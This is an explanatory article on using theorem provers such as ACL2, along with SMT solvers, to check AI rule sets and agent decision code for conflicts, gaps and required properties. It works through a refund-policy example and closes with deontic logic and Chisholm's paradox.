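# Formal verification of AI rule sets and agent logic with theorem provers such as ACL2

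## What a theorem prover proves, and how ACL2 works

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that a system meets a stated requirement. An engineer writes a *model* (a mathematical description of the system) and a *specification* (a formal statement of what the system must do or never do). The engineer then shows that the model satisfies the specification with the help of a *theorem prover*, software that checks proofs in a formal logic and helps find them.

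Chip designers used such proofs long before anyone applied them to AI. Two kinds of AI software suit the method. A *rule set* is a finite list of conditions and the resulting decisions, such as the rules a bank's software uses to refuse loans. An *agent* is a program that repeatedly observes, decides and acts. In many current agents, a language model proposes actions and ordinary code selects which to carry out. It is much easier to prove things about the ordinary code than about the model.

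ACL2, short for "A Computational Logic for Applicative Common Lisp", comes from the University of Texas at Austin. *ACL2 Version 8.7* (Kaufmann and Moore, 2026) describes it as a logic and programming language for modelling computer systems, together with a tool for proving properties of the models. It is the latest in a family of provers begun by Robert Boyer and J Strother Moore, which won its developers the ACM Software System Award in 2005.

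### Testing and proof

A test runs a program on one input and compares the result with the right answer, so it checks only that input. Sometimes a large computer can test every possible input. A rule set with forty yes-or-no conditions, for example, has about 1.1 trillion. But if the input also includes a list of past transactions that may have any length, the number of possible inputs is infinite.

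A toy machine in the ACL2 documentation shows how a proof gets past this. A function mc takes a state of the machine and a number n, and returns the state after n steps. Start the machine with the numbers 5 and 7 and a program for multiplying, run it for 29 steps, and the answer register z holds 35. That is a test. Now leave the second number open and call it y. ACL2 can still simplify the expression, and the result is y + y + y + y + y, which covers every y but only a single value of the first number. The theorem covers both:

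for all natural numbers x and y: lookup(z, mc(start(x, y), clock(x))) = x · y

Here start(x, y) is the state with the two numbers loaded, and clock(x) is the number of steps the program needs for x.

Every result in this field has the form "if the assumptions hold, every run of the model satisfies the specification." In the example, the assumptions are that x and y are natural numbers and that the machine begins in the state start(x, y). The model is mc, and the specification is that z ends up holding the product of x and y. The theorem does not apply to a physical machine whose wiring differs from mc, and it does not help a user who needed the sum instead of the product. For AI systems, building an accurate model and choosing the right specification are often harder than finding the proof.

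Specifications come in two broad kinds. A *safety property* states that something bad never happens, such as the agent deleting a file outside its own folder. A *liveness property* states that something good eventually happens, such as every request getting an answer. A finite record of a run can show that a safety property was violated, but it can't refute a liveness property, because the answer might still come. Both kinds matter, since an agent that does nothing satisfies every requirement of the form "never do X". Engineers often replace "eventually" with a deadline, such as an answer within ten steps. This turns the requirement into a safety property, because a finite record can show a missed deadline. The multiplier theorem is also stronger than "eventually", since clock(x) specifies when the answer arrives.

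### Definitions and termination in ACL2

ACL2 users write the model as functions in a subset of Lisp, a programming language in which function calls are written as lists in parentheses with the function's name first. The subset is "applicative", meaning its functions have no side effects and always return the same value for the same arguments. They therefore behave like mathematical functions, so the same code can be run as a program and reasoned from as a set of equations.

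The running example in the ACL2 documentation is a function that joins two lists using four primitives. (cons a x) puts the item a at the front of the list x, (car x) is the first item of x, (cdr x) is the rest of x, and (endp x) is true when x has no items left.

```
(defun app (x y)
  (if (endp x)
      y
    (cons (car x) (app (cdr x) y))))
```

The function that joins list x to list y returns y if x is empty. Otherwise, it joins the rest of x to y and puts the first item of x on the front of the result. Joining (1 2) to (3 4) gives (1 2 3 4).

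The definition of app is recursive. In ACL2's logic a definition is a new axiom, and a bad axiom can introduce a contradiction. ACL2's *About the Admission of Recursive Definitions* gives the example of a proposed definition in which app(x, y) equals *not* app(x, y). No value equals its own negation, so the equation is a contradiction, and every statement would follow from it, including the statement that a given agent is safe. ACL2 therefore admits a recursive function only after a proof that the recursion ends. Course notes from Northeastern University explain that this proof is enough, apart from some simple checks, because some function satisfies any recursive equation that terminates, so the new axiom cannot introduce a contradiction.

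The termination proof needs a *measure*, a quantity that shrinks with each recursive call. Suppose a function f stops when test(x) is true and otherwise calls itself on d(x). For a measure m, ACL2 requires two theorems:

1. m(x) is always an ordinal.
2. If test(x) is false, then m(d(x)) < m(x).

The ordinals extend the natural numbers and, like them, contain no infinite decreasing sequence, so a measure that keeps decreasing must eventually stop. For app, the measure is the size of the first list, which loses an item at every call. ACL2 finds this measure automatically, but the user supplies one for more complicated functions.

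This requirement affects how people model agents. An agent that should run indefinitely has no measure that decreases to a stopping point, so a direct transcription of its endless loop would fail the termination check. The usual solution, which the toy machine uses, is to define a single step as a function, define mc(s, n) as n steps from state s, and use n as the measure. A theorem about mc(s, n) for every n then covers every finite stretch of the endless run.

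Functions in ACL2's logic are total, meaning that they have a value for every argument. The number 7 is not a list, but by the definition above (app 7 27) equals 27, because 7 has no items. Lisp programmers would rather see an error, so a function can also have a *guard*, a condition describing the arguments it is meant for. Guards are not part of the defining axioms, but ACL2 can prove separately that a program never calls a function outside its guard.

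### A small proof by induction

Join (1 2), (3 4) and (5 6), starting from the left pair or from the right pair, and the result is the same. Perhaps that holds for any three lists. Typing the equation into ACL2 with variables in place of the lists produces an error message, because there is nothing definite to compute. As the ACL2 documentation has it, nobody can evaluate a form on infinitely many cases, but one can prove it a theorem. The command for that is defthm:

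```
(defthm app-assoc
  (equal (app (app x y) z)
         (app x (app y z))))
```

ACL2 first tries to simplify the formula, and when that fails it looks for an induction. An induction on lists proves a statement for the empty list, then proves that if the statement holds for the rest of a list, it holds for the whole list. Every list is a finite number of items added to an empty one, so the statement holds for all lists. ACL2 uses the recursive functions in the formula to choose which of the three variables to induct on. The function app takes apart its first argument and leaves its second unchanged. ACL2 picks x because it appears only as a first argument. The variable y is the first argument in (app y z) but the second in (app x y), where an induction on y would get stuck.

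In the base case, x is empty. By the definition of app, (app x y) is y, so the left side is (app y z). The right side, (app x (app y z)), is also (app y z).

**Induction step.** Suppose x is not empty, and suppose the equation already holds with (cdr x) in place of x. This second supposition is the induction hypothesis. Then:

```
(app (app x y) z)
= (app (cons (car x) (app (cdr x) y)) z)    definition of app
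= (cons (car x) (app (app (cdr x) y) z))    definition of app
= (cons (car x) (app (cdr x) (app y z)))    induction hypothesis
= (app x (app y z))                         definition of app
```

That completes the proof. In *The End of the Flying Tour*, Kaufmann and Moore print ACL2's own version of it, which uses about a dozen small simplifications for the induction step and took a tenth of a second on the machines of the time.

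The measure used to admit app also justifies the induction. Both arguments depend on the first list getting smaller, so the induction can reuse the termination proof.

Nearly every line of the proof replaces one expression with an equal one. This is called *rewriting*, and it is most of what ACL2 does. Once the user has proved app-assoc, ACL2 stores it as a rewrite rule and from then on replaces any expression matching the equation's left side with the corresponding right side. Kaufmann and Moore follow it with an equation about seven lists nested in two different ways. ACL2 proves this equation without induction, by applying the rule until the two sides are identical. If the user also stored the reversed equation as a rule, ACL2 would keep rewriting the same expressions back and forth without end.

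Most of the work in using ACL2 is choosing which smaller theorems (lemmas) to prove first, so that ACL2 can use them as rules when it attempts the hard theorem. Kaufmann and Moore say that ACL2's main job is to prevent logical mistakes, and that the user must supply the insight into why the property holds. They expected a graduate in computer science or mathematics to need several months to become effective. ACL2 also has commands that skip a proof or add an axiom, so anyone relying on a result should check that its author used neither.

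### Searching for counterexamples

Much of what users try to prove is false, most often because they have left out an assumption. A failed proof attempt doesn't show that a statement is false, because ACL2 can fail to prove true statements. The ACL2 Sedan, an extension that Panagiotis Manolios and his research group maintain, therefore also searches for counterexamples.

The ACL2 manual's examples for the Sedan's test? command include the conjecture that reversing a list twice gives back the original. The conjecture is false as written, because the formula doesn't require its variable x to be a list and functions in ACL2 are total. Reversing 7 gives the empty list, and reversing that gives the empty list again, not 7. Adding the assumption that x is a proper list makes the conjecture a theorem.

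Random testing alone would be a weak method, because randomly chosen values of x and y will almost never satisfy an assumption such as "x is the square of y". The Sedan combines testing with deduction. It chooses a value for one variable, uses the prover to work out what follows for the others, and backtracks if it finds a conflict. It works better when it has a description of the data, so the ACL2 manual page *Cgen* advises users to declare their data types. Chamarthi and Manolios describe a fully automatic use of the same machinery, which returns a concrete counterexample, a formal proof or, failing both, a summary of the analysis. A summary leaves the question open, since failing to find a counterexample does not prove the conjecture. Northeastern University's *Using Counterexample Generation and Theory Exploration To Suggest Missing Hypotheses* presents DrLA, a tool that also proposes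 the assumption that would make the statement true.

For rule sets, a counterexample may be the most useful output. A bank that learns its rules are inconsistent wants to see an applicant whom the rules both accept and refuse.

### More automatic tools, and other provers

An *SMT solver* is an automatic tool that decides whether a formula over numbers, strings and similar data can be made true. To prove a property, the user asks the solver to find an input that satisfies the assumptions but breaks the specification. If the solver establishes that none exists, the property holds for every input. Because no person has to guide the proof, solvers are suitable for checks during operation. *Return of the Theorem* (Meijer, 2026) proposes using them to compare each plan an AI agent produces with a company's formalized business rules before the agent may act on it. Solvers are reliable on certain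 kinds of formula, such as linear arithmetic, but on others they may run out of time or return "unknown". The theorem about app is beyond their usual methods because it needs induction. A solver can unfold the definition for lists of particular lengths, but that doesn't prove the theorem for lists of every length.

*Model checking* is verification by automatically exploring the reachable states of a model. If a model checker finds a bad state, it shows the user the steps that led there. Model checkers can handle liveness as well as safety, but the number of states can be a problem, since ten components with ten states each have ten billion combinations. Cubicle, a model checker for systems with an arbitrary number of participants, explores small finite instances and uses them to derive invariants (properties true at the start and preserved by every step) that help prove the general case.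 Even so, Sylvain Conchon explains in a 2026 talk abstract in NETYS's *Workshop Program* that the standard ways of exploring soon run into this "state explosion" and miss critical states.

An interactive theorem prover, which a person or an AI system guides, can handle lists of any length and runs of any number of steps, and its language can express almost any mathematical property. But it needs the most help of the tools described here. In practice, different kinds of tools can be combined, and one paper from the 2025 ACL2 workshop connects the ACL2 Sedan to the SMT solver Z3.

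Interactive provers also differ from one another. ACL2's logic is first-order, so its variables stand for data and never for functions. Users recover some of the lost generality with constrained functions, which are specified only by a few stated properties. Ordinary ACL2 has fractions but no irrational numbers; a variant, ACL2(r), adds the reals.

Four other provers come up repeatedly in work on AI:

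- Isabelle/HOL is an interactive prover for higher-order logic, in which variables may stand for functions, and the Isabelle Workshop marked Isabelle's fortieth anniversary in July 2026.
- Lean is a programming language and prover in one, with a logic in which a type can express a detailed specification, and mathematicians use it heavily.
- Rocq, which was called Coq until recently, has a closely related logic and a long record in proofs about software.
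- Imandra works on programs in a subset of the language OCaml and, much like the Sedan, combines automatic induction with a search for counterexamples.

The amount of human help these provers need is changing quickly. *Agentic Verification of Software Systems* (2025) describes AutoRocq, an AI agent that looks up relevant lemmas in Rocq as it builds a proof and revises the steps that Rocq rejects. Its developers tested it on standard verification benchmarks and on modules of the Linux kernel. *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026) reports that, by July 2026, a general-purpose coding agent had proved every lemma it was given in Coq without help from a human expert. Some of those lemmas belong to separation logic for concurrent programs, where proofs are notoriously laborious. The same set-up then proved all 72 lemmas chosen from an unfinished Lean library. Because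 the prover checks each proof, a proof found by an AI system is as valid as one written by a person. People still have to state the theorem correctly, which means getting the model, the assumptions and the specification right.

These successes are in Rocq and Lean, and ACL2 may be harder for an AI agent to use. *Verification and Attack Synthesis for Network Protocols* (2025), which used ACL2 extensively, reports that ACL2 users can't search for existing theorems by meaning, that many useful theorems are missing from the documentation, and that rules from different libraries can conflict.

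### Where the evidence comes from

Published work that applies ACL2 to AI agents is scarce. The main forum for ACL2 research is a workshop held about every eighteen months. *Proceedings of the 18th International Workshop on the ACL2 Theorem Prover* (Coglio and Swords, 2023) contains thirteen papers, and *Proceedings of the 19th International Workshop on the ACL2 Theorem Prover* (Gamboa and Manolios, 2025) contains eleven. Of these, ten concern hardware, network protocols or program code, six formalize mathematics, and eight improve the prover or its tools. Judging by their titles, none is about an AI agent. At the 2025 workshop, Swarat Chaudhuri gave an invited talk on using machine learning to help write specifications and proofs. The organizers scheduled the next workshop for 16 to 18 November 2026 in Menlo Park, and the ACL2 Workshop's *20th International Workshop on the ACL2 Theorem Prover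 and Its Applications* lists the proceedings as still to appear.

Much of the direct evidence on agents therefore comes from other provers, and it is recent there too. *Lean4Agent* (2026), which models the workflows of language-model agents in Lean, claims to be the first work to describe agent behaviour in a language of that kind. The ACL2 literature is still relevant because a processor or a participant in a network protocol, like an agent, holds a state, receives an input, and computes an action and a new state. A proof about such a step function carries over with little change to an agent's decision code, but not to a language model inside the agent, because nobody has a definition of the model short enough to reason about in this way.

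## Finding conflicts and gaps in a set of rules

Consider an agent that handles refund requests for a shop. Its developer has written three rules:

- Approve the refund if the customer is verified and the amount is at most 100.
- Refuse it if the account is flagged.
- Escalate it to an employee if the amount exceeds 100.

Each rule is sensible by itself, but together they require both an approval and a refusal when a verified customer with a flagged account asks for 50. They give no decision when an unverified customer with an unflagged account asks for the same amount. A *conflict* is an input that triggers two incompatible decisions, and a *gap* is an input that triggers none. A careful reader can find both by hand in a set this small, but a set of 300 rules has 44,850 pairs to compare.

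### The checks as formulas

Write x for an input, c1(x), …, cn(x) for the conditions of the n rules, and D(x) for the decision that the whole rule set returns. Each check is a search for an input that makes some formula true:

| Check | Search for an input x such that | If no such x exists |
|---|---|---|
| Conflict | ci(x) and cj(x), where rules i and j have incompatible decisions | rules i and j never conflict |
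| Gap | not c1(x) and … and not cn(x) | every input gets a decision |
| Unreachable rule | ck(x), and no earlier rule's condition holds | rule k never decides anything |
| Redundancy | D(x) changes when rule k is deleted | rule k is redundant |
| Equivalence | D(x) ≠ D′(x), where D′ is another version of the rules | the versions always agree |
| Required property P | P(x, D(x)) is false | every decision has the property |

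The formula for an unreachable rule assumes that the software tries the rules in order and stops at the first that applies. In practice, every search also assumes which inputs can occur, for example that the amount is positive. People have to supply that assumption and specify which decisions are incompatible. For example, "refuse" is incompatible with "approve" but not with "notify the customer". Duties and permissions can also conflict in subtler ways.

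### The refund rules in ACL2

In ACL2 the three conditions become three small functions. ACL2 writes true as t and false as nil.

```
(defun approve-if (verified amount)
  (and verified (<= amount 100)))

(defun refuse-if (flagged)
  flagged)

(defun escalate-if (amount)
  (> amount 100))
```

The command thm tries to prove a formula without storing it as a rewrite rule. This one states that approval and refusal never conflict:

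```
(thm (not (and (approve-if verified amount)
               (refuse-if flagged))))
```

The proof fails, and the input (verified, flagged, 50) shows why. With escalate-if in place of refuse-if the formula is a theorem, since no amount is both at most 100 and over 100. For the gap check, ACL2 has to prove that at least one condition always holds:

```
(thm (or (approve-if verified amount)
         (refuse-if flagged)
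         (escalate-if amount)))
```

This fails too. The simplified goal amounts to "if the customer is unverified and the account is unflagged, then the amount exceeds 100", which is false for the input (unverified, unflagged, 50).

The amount can take infinitely many values, but the rules only ever compare it with 100, so eight cases cover everything:

| Verified | Flagged | Over 100 | Rules that apply | Decision after the repair below |
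|---|---|---|---|---|
| yes | yes | no | approve, refuse (conflict) | refuse |
| yes | yes | yes | refuse, escalate (conflict) | refuse |
| yes | no | no | approve | approve |
| yes | no | yes | escalate | escalate |
| no | yes | no | refuse | refuse |
| no | yes | yes | refuse, escalate (conflict) | refuse |
| no | no | no | none (gap) | refuse |
| no | no | yes | escalate | escalate |

Two of the three conflicts are between refusing and escalating. The shop might not mind those, if it wants an employee to look at large requests from flagged accounts. Suppose it prefers a plain refusal. The developer can then repair the rules by putting them in order and adding a default:

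```
(defun decide (verified flagged amount)
  (cond (flagged        'refuse)
        ((> amount 100) 'escalate)
        (verified       'approve)
        (t              'refuse)))
```

Lisp's cond checks the lines from the top and returns the decision on the first line whose condition is true. The condition t on the last line is always true.

A function returns exactly one value for each input, so decide can have no conflicts or gaps. That is a cheap guarantee. Any order of the lines would have provided it, including one that approves refunds before it looks at the flag, and the default covers a case the developer forgot just as readily as one the developer meant to refuse. It therefore makes sense to run the conflict and gap checks on the separate conditions first, before anyone chooses an order. Once the rules are in order, the developer needs a property that a bad order would violate:

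```
(thm (implies (equal (decide verified flagged amount) 'approve)
              (and verified
                   (not flagged)
                   (<= amount 100))))
```

ACL2 proves this by expanding the definition of decide and considering its four lines. Three of them return something other than approve, which contradicts the assumption, so ACL2 has nothing to prove for them. The remaining line returns approve only if the customer is verified, and the function reaches that line only if the account is unflagged and the amount is not over 100. If the developer had put the verified line at the top, (verified, flagged, 50) would have been a counterexample.

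A function that refuses everyone also satisfies this theorem, so the shop needs to prove the converse too, that a verified customer with an unflagged account who asks for at most 100 gets an approval. ACL2 proves this the same way.

The theorem still permits some odd approvals. It places no lower bound on the amount, so decide approves a refund of −50. ACL2's comparisons also treat anything that is not a number as 0, so a verified customer could get approval for a refund of "fifty". A guard requiring a positive number would exclude both cases, provided the surrounding code respects it.

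Suppose that a colleague, or a coding agent, now rewrites the function:

```
(defun decide-2 (verified flagged amount)
  (cond ((and verified (not flagged) (<= amount 100)) 'approve)
        ((and (not flagged) (> amount 100))           'escalate)
        (t                                            'refuse)))
```

ACL2 can prove that decide and decide-2 return the same decision for every input. The advantage of decide-2 is that its first two conditions exclude each other, so swapping them can't break it. But equivalence is a reason to trust one version only if the other is already trusted, because if decide is wrong for an input, decide-2 is wrong for it too.

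The other two checks matter most when a rule set grows. If someone adds "escalate if the account is flagged and the amount exceeds 1,000" at the end of decide, the new line is unreachable, because the first line has already refused every flagged request. This is probably a mistake, since whoever added the line wanted an employee to see those requests. The line "refuse if the customer is unverified", placed just above the default, would apply to some requests but would be redundant, because the default would refuse them anyway.

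Any change to the definitions means running the proofs again. In teaching notes on ACL2, Dillinger defines "too big" as over 1,000 and proves that every number above 20,000 is too big. If the threshold is raised to 1,000,000, the same formula is false, because 30,000 is above 20,000 but is not too big.

### Conflicting decisions and inconsistent axioms

A conflict between two rules is a defect in the policy that a prover can reason about. An inconsistency among the axioms of the logic is far more serious because it makes every proof worthless. Conflicting rules can cause either problem, depending on how the developer enters them into the prover.

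The functions above cannot make the logic inconsistent, however foolish the policy they express, because ACL2 has admitted each one as a definition. But a developer could also declare a function named decision, leave it undefined, and state the rules as axioms about it:

```
(defstub decision (* * *) => *)

(defaxiom approve-rule
  (implies (and verified (<= amount 100))
           (equal (decision verified flagged amount) 'approve)))

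(defaxiom refuse-rule
  (implies flagged
           (equal (decision verified flagged amount) 'refuse)))
```

The rules contradict each other, even though they look like a faithful transcription of the policy. When a verified customer with a flagged account asks for 50, approve-rule makes the decision equal to approve and refuse-rule makes it equal to refuse. ACL2 can therefore prove that approve equals refuse, and it can also prove that they are different symbols.

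Every statement now follows from the two axioms, as it did from the self-negating definition in the previous section. The axioms imply that some statement S is both true and false. Because S is true, "S or Q" is true for any statement Q, and because S is also false, Q must be true. Logicians call this explosion. The Internet Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Paraconsistent Logic* describes logics designed to avoid it, but ACL2's logic is not one of them. The two axioms therefore prove both "the agent never approves a refund for a flagged account" and its opposite. A developer who tries to prove only the first gets a valid proof and no warning that the axioms conflict.

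ACL2's manual page *Add an axiom* strongly recommends against adding any axioms, and its example of one equates t (true) with nil (false). It recommends using recursive definitions instead, or the encapsulate command, which introduces constrained functions. With encapsulate, the user must first supply an example function with the stated properties. No function satisfies both refund rules at (verified, flagged, 50), so ACL2 would reject them, revealing the conflict before it could do any damage.

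Axioms with a gap are still consistent, but they don't determine the decision in every case. In a case they leave open, ACL2 can prove neither that the agent approves the request nor that it refuses.

### Rule checkers for expert systems

These checks are older than ACL2. In the 1970s and 1980s, many AI researchers built expert systems, programs that reach conclusions by applying rules collected from human specialists. One of them, ONCOCIN, advised Stanford physicians on treating cancer patients under experimental protocols. *An Approach to Verifying Completeness and Consistency in a Rule-Based Expert System* (Suwa, Scott and Shortliffe, 1982) describes a program that checked ONCOCIN's rules without running any patient cases. Preece's 1994 survey, *Validation of Knowledge-Based Systems*, reports that this program is generally considered the first tool of its kind.

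The program collected all the rules that set the same quantity in the same context, listed the conditions they used, and built a table of every combination of those conditions, like the refund table above. One table covered seven rules for the dose of the drug cytoxan. The rules depended on whether the patient's blood counts called for a lower dose, whether this was the first cycle of chemotherapy, and whether it was the first cycle after significant radiation, which again makes eight combinations. In one combination, two rules conflicted because one reduced the dose for poor blood counts and the other did not. In another, two rules gave the same result. Two combinations had no rule. For a gap, the program could draft the missing rule in English and leave the dose blank for the experts to fill in.

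Suwa and colleagues held that only conflicts are certain to be errors. Two rules with the same result may do no harm until someone changes one and forgets the other. A combination of conditions without a rule may never occur, but the program could not detect that. If some rules mention amounts over 50 and others mention amounts over 100, a table of this kind includes an impossible row for amounts over 100 that are not over 50. The ONCOCIN team planned to let experts record constraints that exclude such combinations. An SMT solver excludes this row by arithmetic.

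Conflicts are harder to find when the conclusion of one rule triggers another. CHECK, a Lockheed program presented in *Checking an Expert Systems Knowledge Base for Consistency and Completeness* (1985), also looked for rules that lead back to themselves and for dead ends. Its successor EVA let experts declare that two facts, such as "male" and "pregnant", exclude each other, then used theorem proving to look for inputs from which the rules would derive both. KB-Reducer, from AT&T Bell Laboratories, found the smallest sets of input facts that lead to each conclusion, then compared the sets for incompatible conclusions. According to Preece, it needed ten hours of processor time for 570 rules and generated 35,000 sets. For n facts there can be up to 3^n sets, because a set can contain each fact, its negation or neither.

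None of the systems that Boeing analysed with a later version came near the worst case, and the tool found various faults in them. COVER, developed at Concordia University and Bell Canada, found faults in systems from NASA, 3M and the British health services, and its simplest checks found the most. Such tools can look for conflicts and redundancies in any rule set, even without a specification of what the rules should achieve. Researchers also tried to prove specific properties of expert systems whose rules update a shared memory. Apart from one IBM project, Preece found only toy examples of this work, such as tic-tac-toe, and named the lack of formal requirements as a serious obstacle.

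### Google's verifier for the Common Expression Language

The Common Expression Language (CEL) is a small language from Google for writing conditions inside other software, such as when a service should accept a request. Google designed it so that expressions run in linear time and change no data. It is deliberately not Turing-complete, so it can't express every possible computation. These limits make CEL programs much easier to analyse than ordinary code.

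Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) announced a verification framework for CEL in August. It presents the framework as a response to AI agents now writing and revising CEL policies, since an agent may fit a policy to the existing unit tests but get other inputs wrong. The framework translates CEL expressions and policies into formulas for the SMT solver Z3, which searches for an input that breaks the requirement. The result is "Verified" if Z3 proves that no such input exists. Otherwise, the user gets "Violated" and the input that Z3 found.

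One of the announcement's examples is an equivalence check. A rule allows ports 80 and 443 in production, and an agent shortens it:

```
(is_prod && port == 80) || (is_prod && port == 443)

is_prod && port == 80 || port == 443
```

In CEL, "and" (&&) binds more tightly than "or" (||), so the shorter version allows port 443 everywhere. The verifier returns the case in which is_prod is false and the port is 443. In another example, a gap check, an engineer assumes that every port is either at most 80 or above 1024. The verifier returns port 81, the first of the 944 ports the engineer overlooked.

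The announcement's longest example is a policy that decides which workloads may run. Like the repaired refund rules, it is an ordered list:

1. Admit the workload if it is privileged and bound for production.
2. Admit it if the requester is an administrator or the request has approval.
3. Otherwise, reject it.

The policy must reject the workload when there is no approval and no administrator. Z3 therefore searches for an input that meets both conditions but is still admitted. Line 2 never applies to such inputs, so the policy admits them exactly when the workload is privileged and bound for production. Z3 returns such a workload, submitted by someone who belongs to no groups. The author could fix the policy by deleting line 1. This is simpler than also requiring approval or an administrator in line 1, which would make the line redundant because line 2 already admits all those workloads.

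The framework can also check whether a request could force an evaluation error, in which case the policy returns no decision at all.

The framework cannot always provide the "mathematical certainty" across all inputs that Google promises. Applications can add their own functions to CEL, and if a possible violation depends on a function that nobody has translated for Z3, the result is "Inconclusive". For nested data, such as lists of lists, the verifier searches only to a depth that the user sets, so the result does not cover deeper data. Google also promises that every reported violation is real, which depends on CEL being translated correctly into formulas.

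Catala is a programming language for turning legislation into code. Its compiler generates formulas that, once proved, rule out both "empty" errors (gaps) and "conflict" errors, according to Catala's *Verification*. Oracle has published a conceptual design in which an analysis tool checks an agent's policy for conflicts, missing cases, unreachable rules and redundancy before deployment. Oracle points out that the decisions also depend on accurate facts at run time. For example, a verified policy still admits the wrong workload if the approval field is wrong.

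When developers intentionally change an agent's permissions, requiring the old and new policies to be fully equivalent is too strict. It is more useful to check containment, meaning whether the new policy allows anything that the old one did not. Watson (2026), in *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents*, uses Z3 for such queries in OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for agents. OpenShell is also adopting Amazon's policy language Cedar. Raman (2026), in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*, says this is partly because comparing two Cedar policies is decidable, which means an algorithm can always settle the question.

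### When a solver is enough

A solver can easily handle every check on the refund rules, because the inputs are two yes-or-no facts and a number, and the conditions compare the number with a constant. Many access and approval policies are similar. A solver is more convenient than ACL2 for these policies, unless a condition needs harder arithmetic, such as multiplying an unknown quantity by an unknown price.

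A proof can sometimes ignore a list in the input. The workload policy searches the requester's groups for "admin", and there may be any number of groups. The policy uses the list only to check whether the requester is an administrator, so a proof can treat that as one unknown yes-or-no fact.

Adding the daily limit that the refund rules lack would be different. The rule would need the sum of the refunds a customer has already received that day, and a function that adds up a list of any length is recursive:

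```
(defun total (refunds)
  (if (endp refunds)
      0
    (+ (car refunds) (total (cdr refunds)))))
```

In practice the agent would store a running total and add each new refund to it. To show that the stored number stays correct, the developer needs a theorem about lists of every length. Here app is the function from the previous section that joins two lists:

```
(thm (equal (total (app x y))
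            (+ (total x) (total y))))
```

If x is the list of earlier refunds and y contains only the new one, the theorem means that adding the new amount to the old total gives the total of the longer list. ACL2 proves it by induction on x. If x is empty, both sides equal (total y). Otherwise, by the definitions and the induction hypothesis, both sides equal the first item of x, plus the total of the rest of x, plus (total y).

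Imandra's *verification commands* let a user either attempt a full proof of such a theorem or run a weaker check that limits how far Imandra unrolls recursive definitions. After the induction, the daily limit is easy to check, because the rule "refuse if the running total plus the amount exceeds 500" treats the running total as an ordinary number, which a solver can handle without help.

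## Rules that state obligations

People and agents can break their rules, whereas the decide function in the refund example cannot, because whatever it returns is the decision. "The company must erase data that it processed unlawfully" is still in force when the company keeps the data. Suppose a developer writes this rule as "if the company processed the data unlawfully, it erases the data", and then records that the company processed a file unlawfully and kept it. The developer meant to describe a violation, but the axioms are now inconsistent because the recorded facts contradict the rule.

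Another option is to add a yes-or-no fact called must-erase, which can be true while the company keeps the data. But ordinary logic doesn't connect this fact with a second one called may-erase. Farjami, Redondi and Valentino (2026) point out in *Logic-Parametric Neuro-Symbolic NLI* that first-order logic needs an extra axiom to get from "you are obliged to submit the assignment" to "you are permitted to submit it". For simple rule sets, a developer can add the missing connections by hand. *A Simple Doxastic Deontic Logic for Norm-Guided Decision Making* (2026) shows that reasoning about obligations reduces to ordinary propositional logic if each obligation applies to a single fact, such as erasing a file. Conditional obligations are harder to handle, especially those that take effect only after someone has broken another obligation.

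### Standard deontic logic

*Deontic logic* is the logic of obligation and permission. It adds an operator O to ordinary logic, so that Op means "it ought to be that p". "p is forbidden" is then O(not p), and "p is permitted" is not O(not p). The standard version has two axioms for O:

- K: if O(p → q) and Op, then Oq.
- D: Op and O(not p) are never both true.

Another rule makes every theorem of logic obligatory, which sounds odd but rules out no behaviour. Axiom D means that obligations cannot contradict each other and, given the definition of permission, that whatever is obligatory is permitted, a step that first-order logic lacked.

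The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Deontic Logic* explains the operator with possible worlds. Relative to any given world, the acceptable worlds are those in which everything obligatory holds. Op is true if p holds in every acceptable world, and p is permitted if it holds in at least one. The logic requires that there always be an acceptable world. Axiom D follows, because if p and "not p" were both obligatory, both would have to hold in that world.

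Axiom D is also a substantive claim about morality. Someone who has promised to be in two places at noon arguably has two obligations and can meet only one. Standard deontic logic cannot represent both obligations without contradiction.

### Chisholm's paradox

In 1963 the philosopher Roderick Chisholm showed that the logic also fails on a case with no real dilemma in it:

1. Jones ought to go and help his neighbours.
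2. It ought to be that he tells them he is coming if he goes.
3. If he stays at home, he ought not to tell them he is coming.
4. He stays at home.

These sentences are jointly sensible, and none of them seems to follow from the others. The third is a *contrary-to-duty obligation*, one that applies when someone has violated another obligation. Duties to apologize, pay a fine or report an incident are of this kind, so an agent that can fail needs them. With g for "Jones goes" and t for "Jones tells them", the obvious translation leads to a contradiction:

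```
1. O g                   premise
2. O (g → t)             premise
3. not g → O (not t)     premise
4. not g                 premise
5. O t                   from 1 and 2, by axiom K
6. O (not t)             from 3 and 4
7. contradiction         from 5 and 6, by axiom D
```

The translation treats the two conditionals differently. In sentence 2 the operator O covers the whole conditional, and in sentence 3 it covers only the second half. Benzmüller, Fuenmayor and Pasetto (2026), in *Mathematical Proof Assistants for Teaching Logic*, had the prover Isabelle/HOL check all four combinations:

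| Sentence 2 | Sentence 3 | Result |
|---|---|---|
| O(g → t) | not g → O(not t) | the four sentences are inconsistent |
| O(g → t) | O(not g → not t) | sentence 3 follows from sentence 1 |
| g → Ot | not g → O(not t) | sentence 2 follows from sentence 4 |
| g → Ot | O(not g → not t) | both of these redundancies |

The redundancies cause problems because, in ordinary logic, "if g, then anything" is true whenever g is false. On the reading g → Ot, Jones's staying at home therefore proves that if he goes he ought to tell his neighbours, and also that if he goes he ought to rob them. The third combination also implies that he ought to go and that he ought not to tell, and therefore that he ought to go without telling. The Internet Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Contrary-to-Duty Paradox* gives a stranger example of the same effect, in which you ought to keep your promise and apologize for breaking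 it.

Giving up axiom D removes the contradiction in the first combination but leaves Jones obliged both to tell and not to tell. No world satisfies both obligations, so no world is acceptable. Every statement then holds in all the acceptable worlds, because there are none, so everything becomes both obligatory and forbidden.

### Obligations with conditions

The usual repair is a new operator, O(q/p), which means "given p, it ought to be that q". In a version by Lennart Åqvist, called system E, a model ranks worlds from better to worse. O(q/p) is true if q holds in all the best worlds among those where p holds. For Jones, a suitable ranking is:

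1. He goes and tells them.
2. He stays at home and does not tell them he is coming.
3. He goes without telling them, or tells them and stays at home.

Jones goes in the best world overall, so he ought to go. He tells his neighbours he is coming in the best world where he goes, so he ought to tell them if he goes. He doesn't tell them in the best world where he stays at home, so he ought not to tell them if he stays. If that last world is the actual one, all four of Chisholm's sentences are true together.

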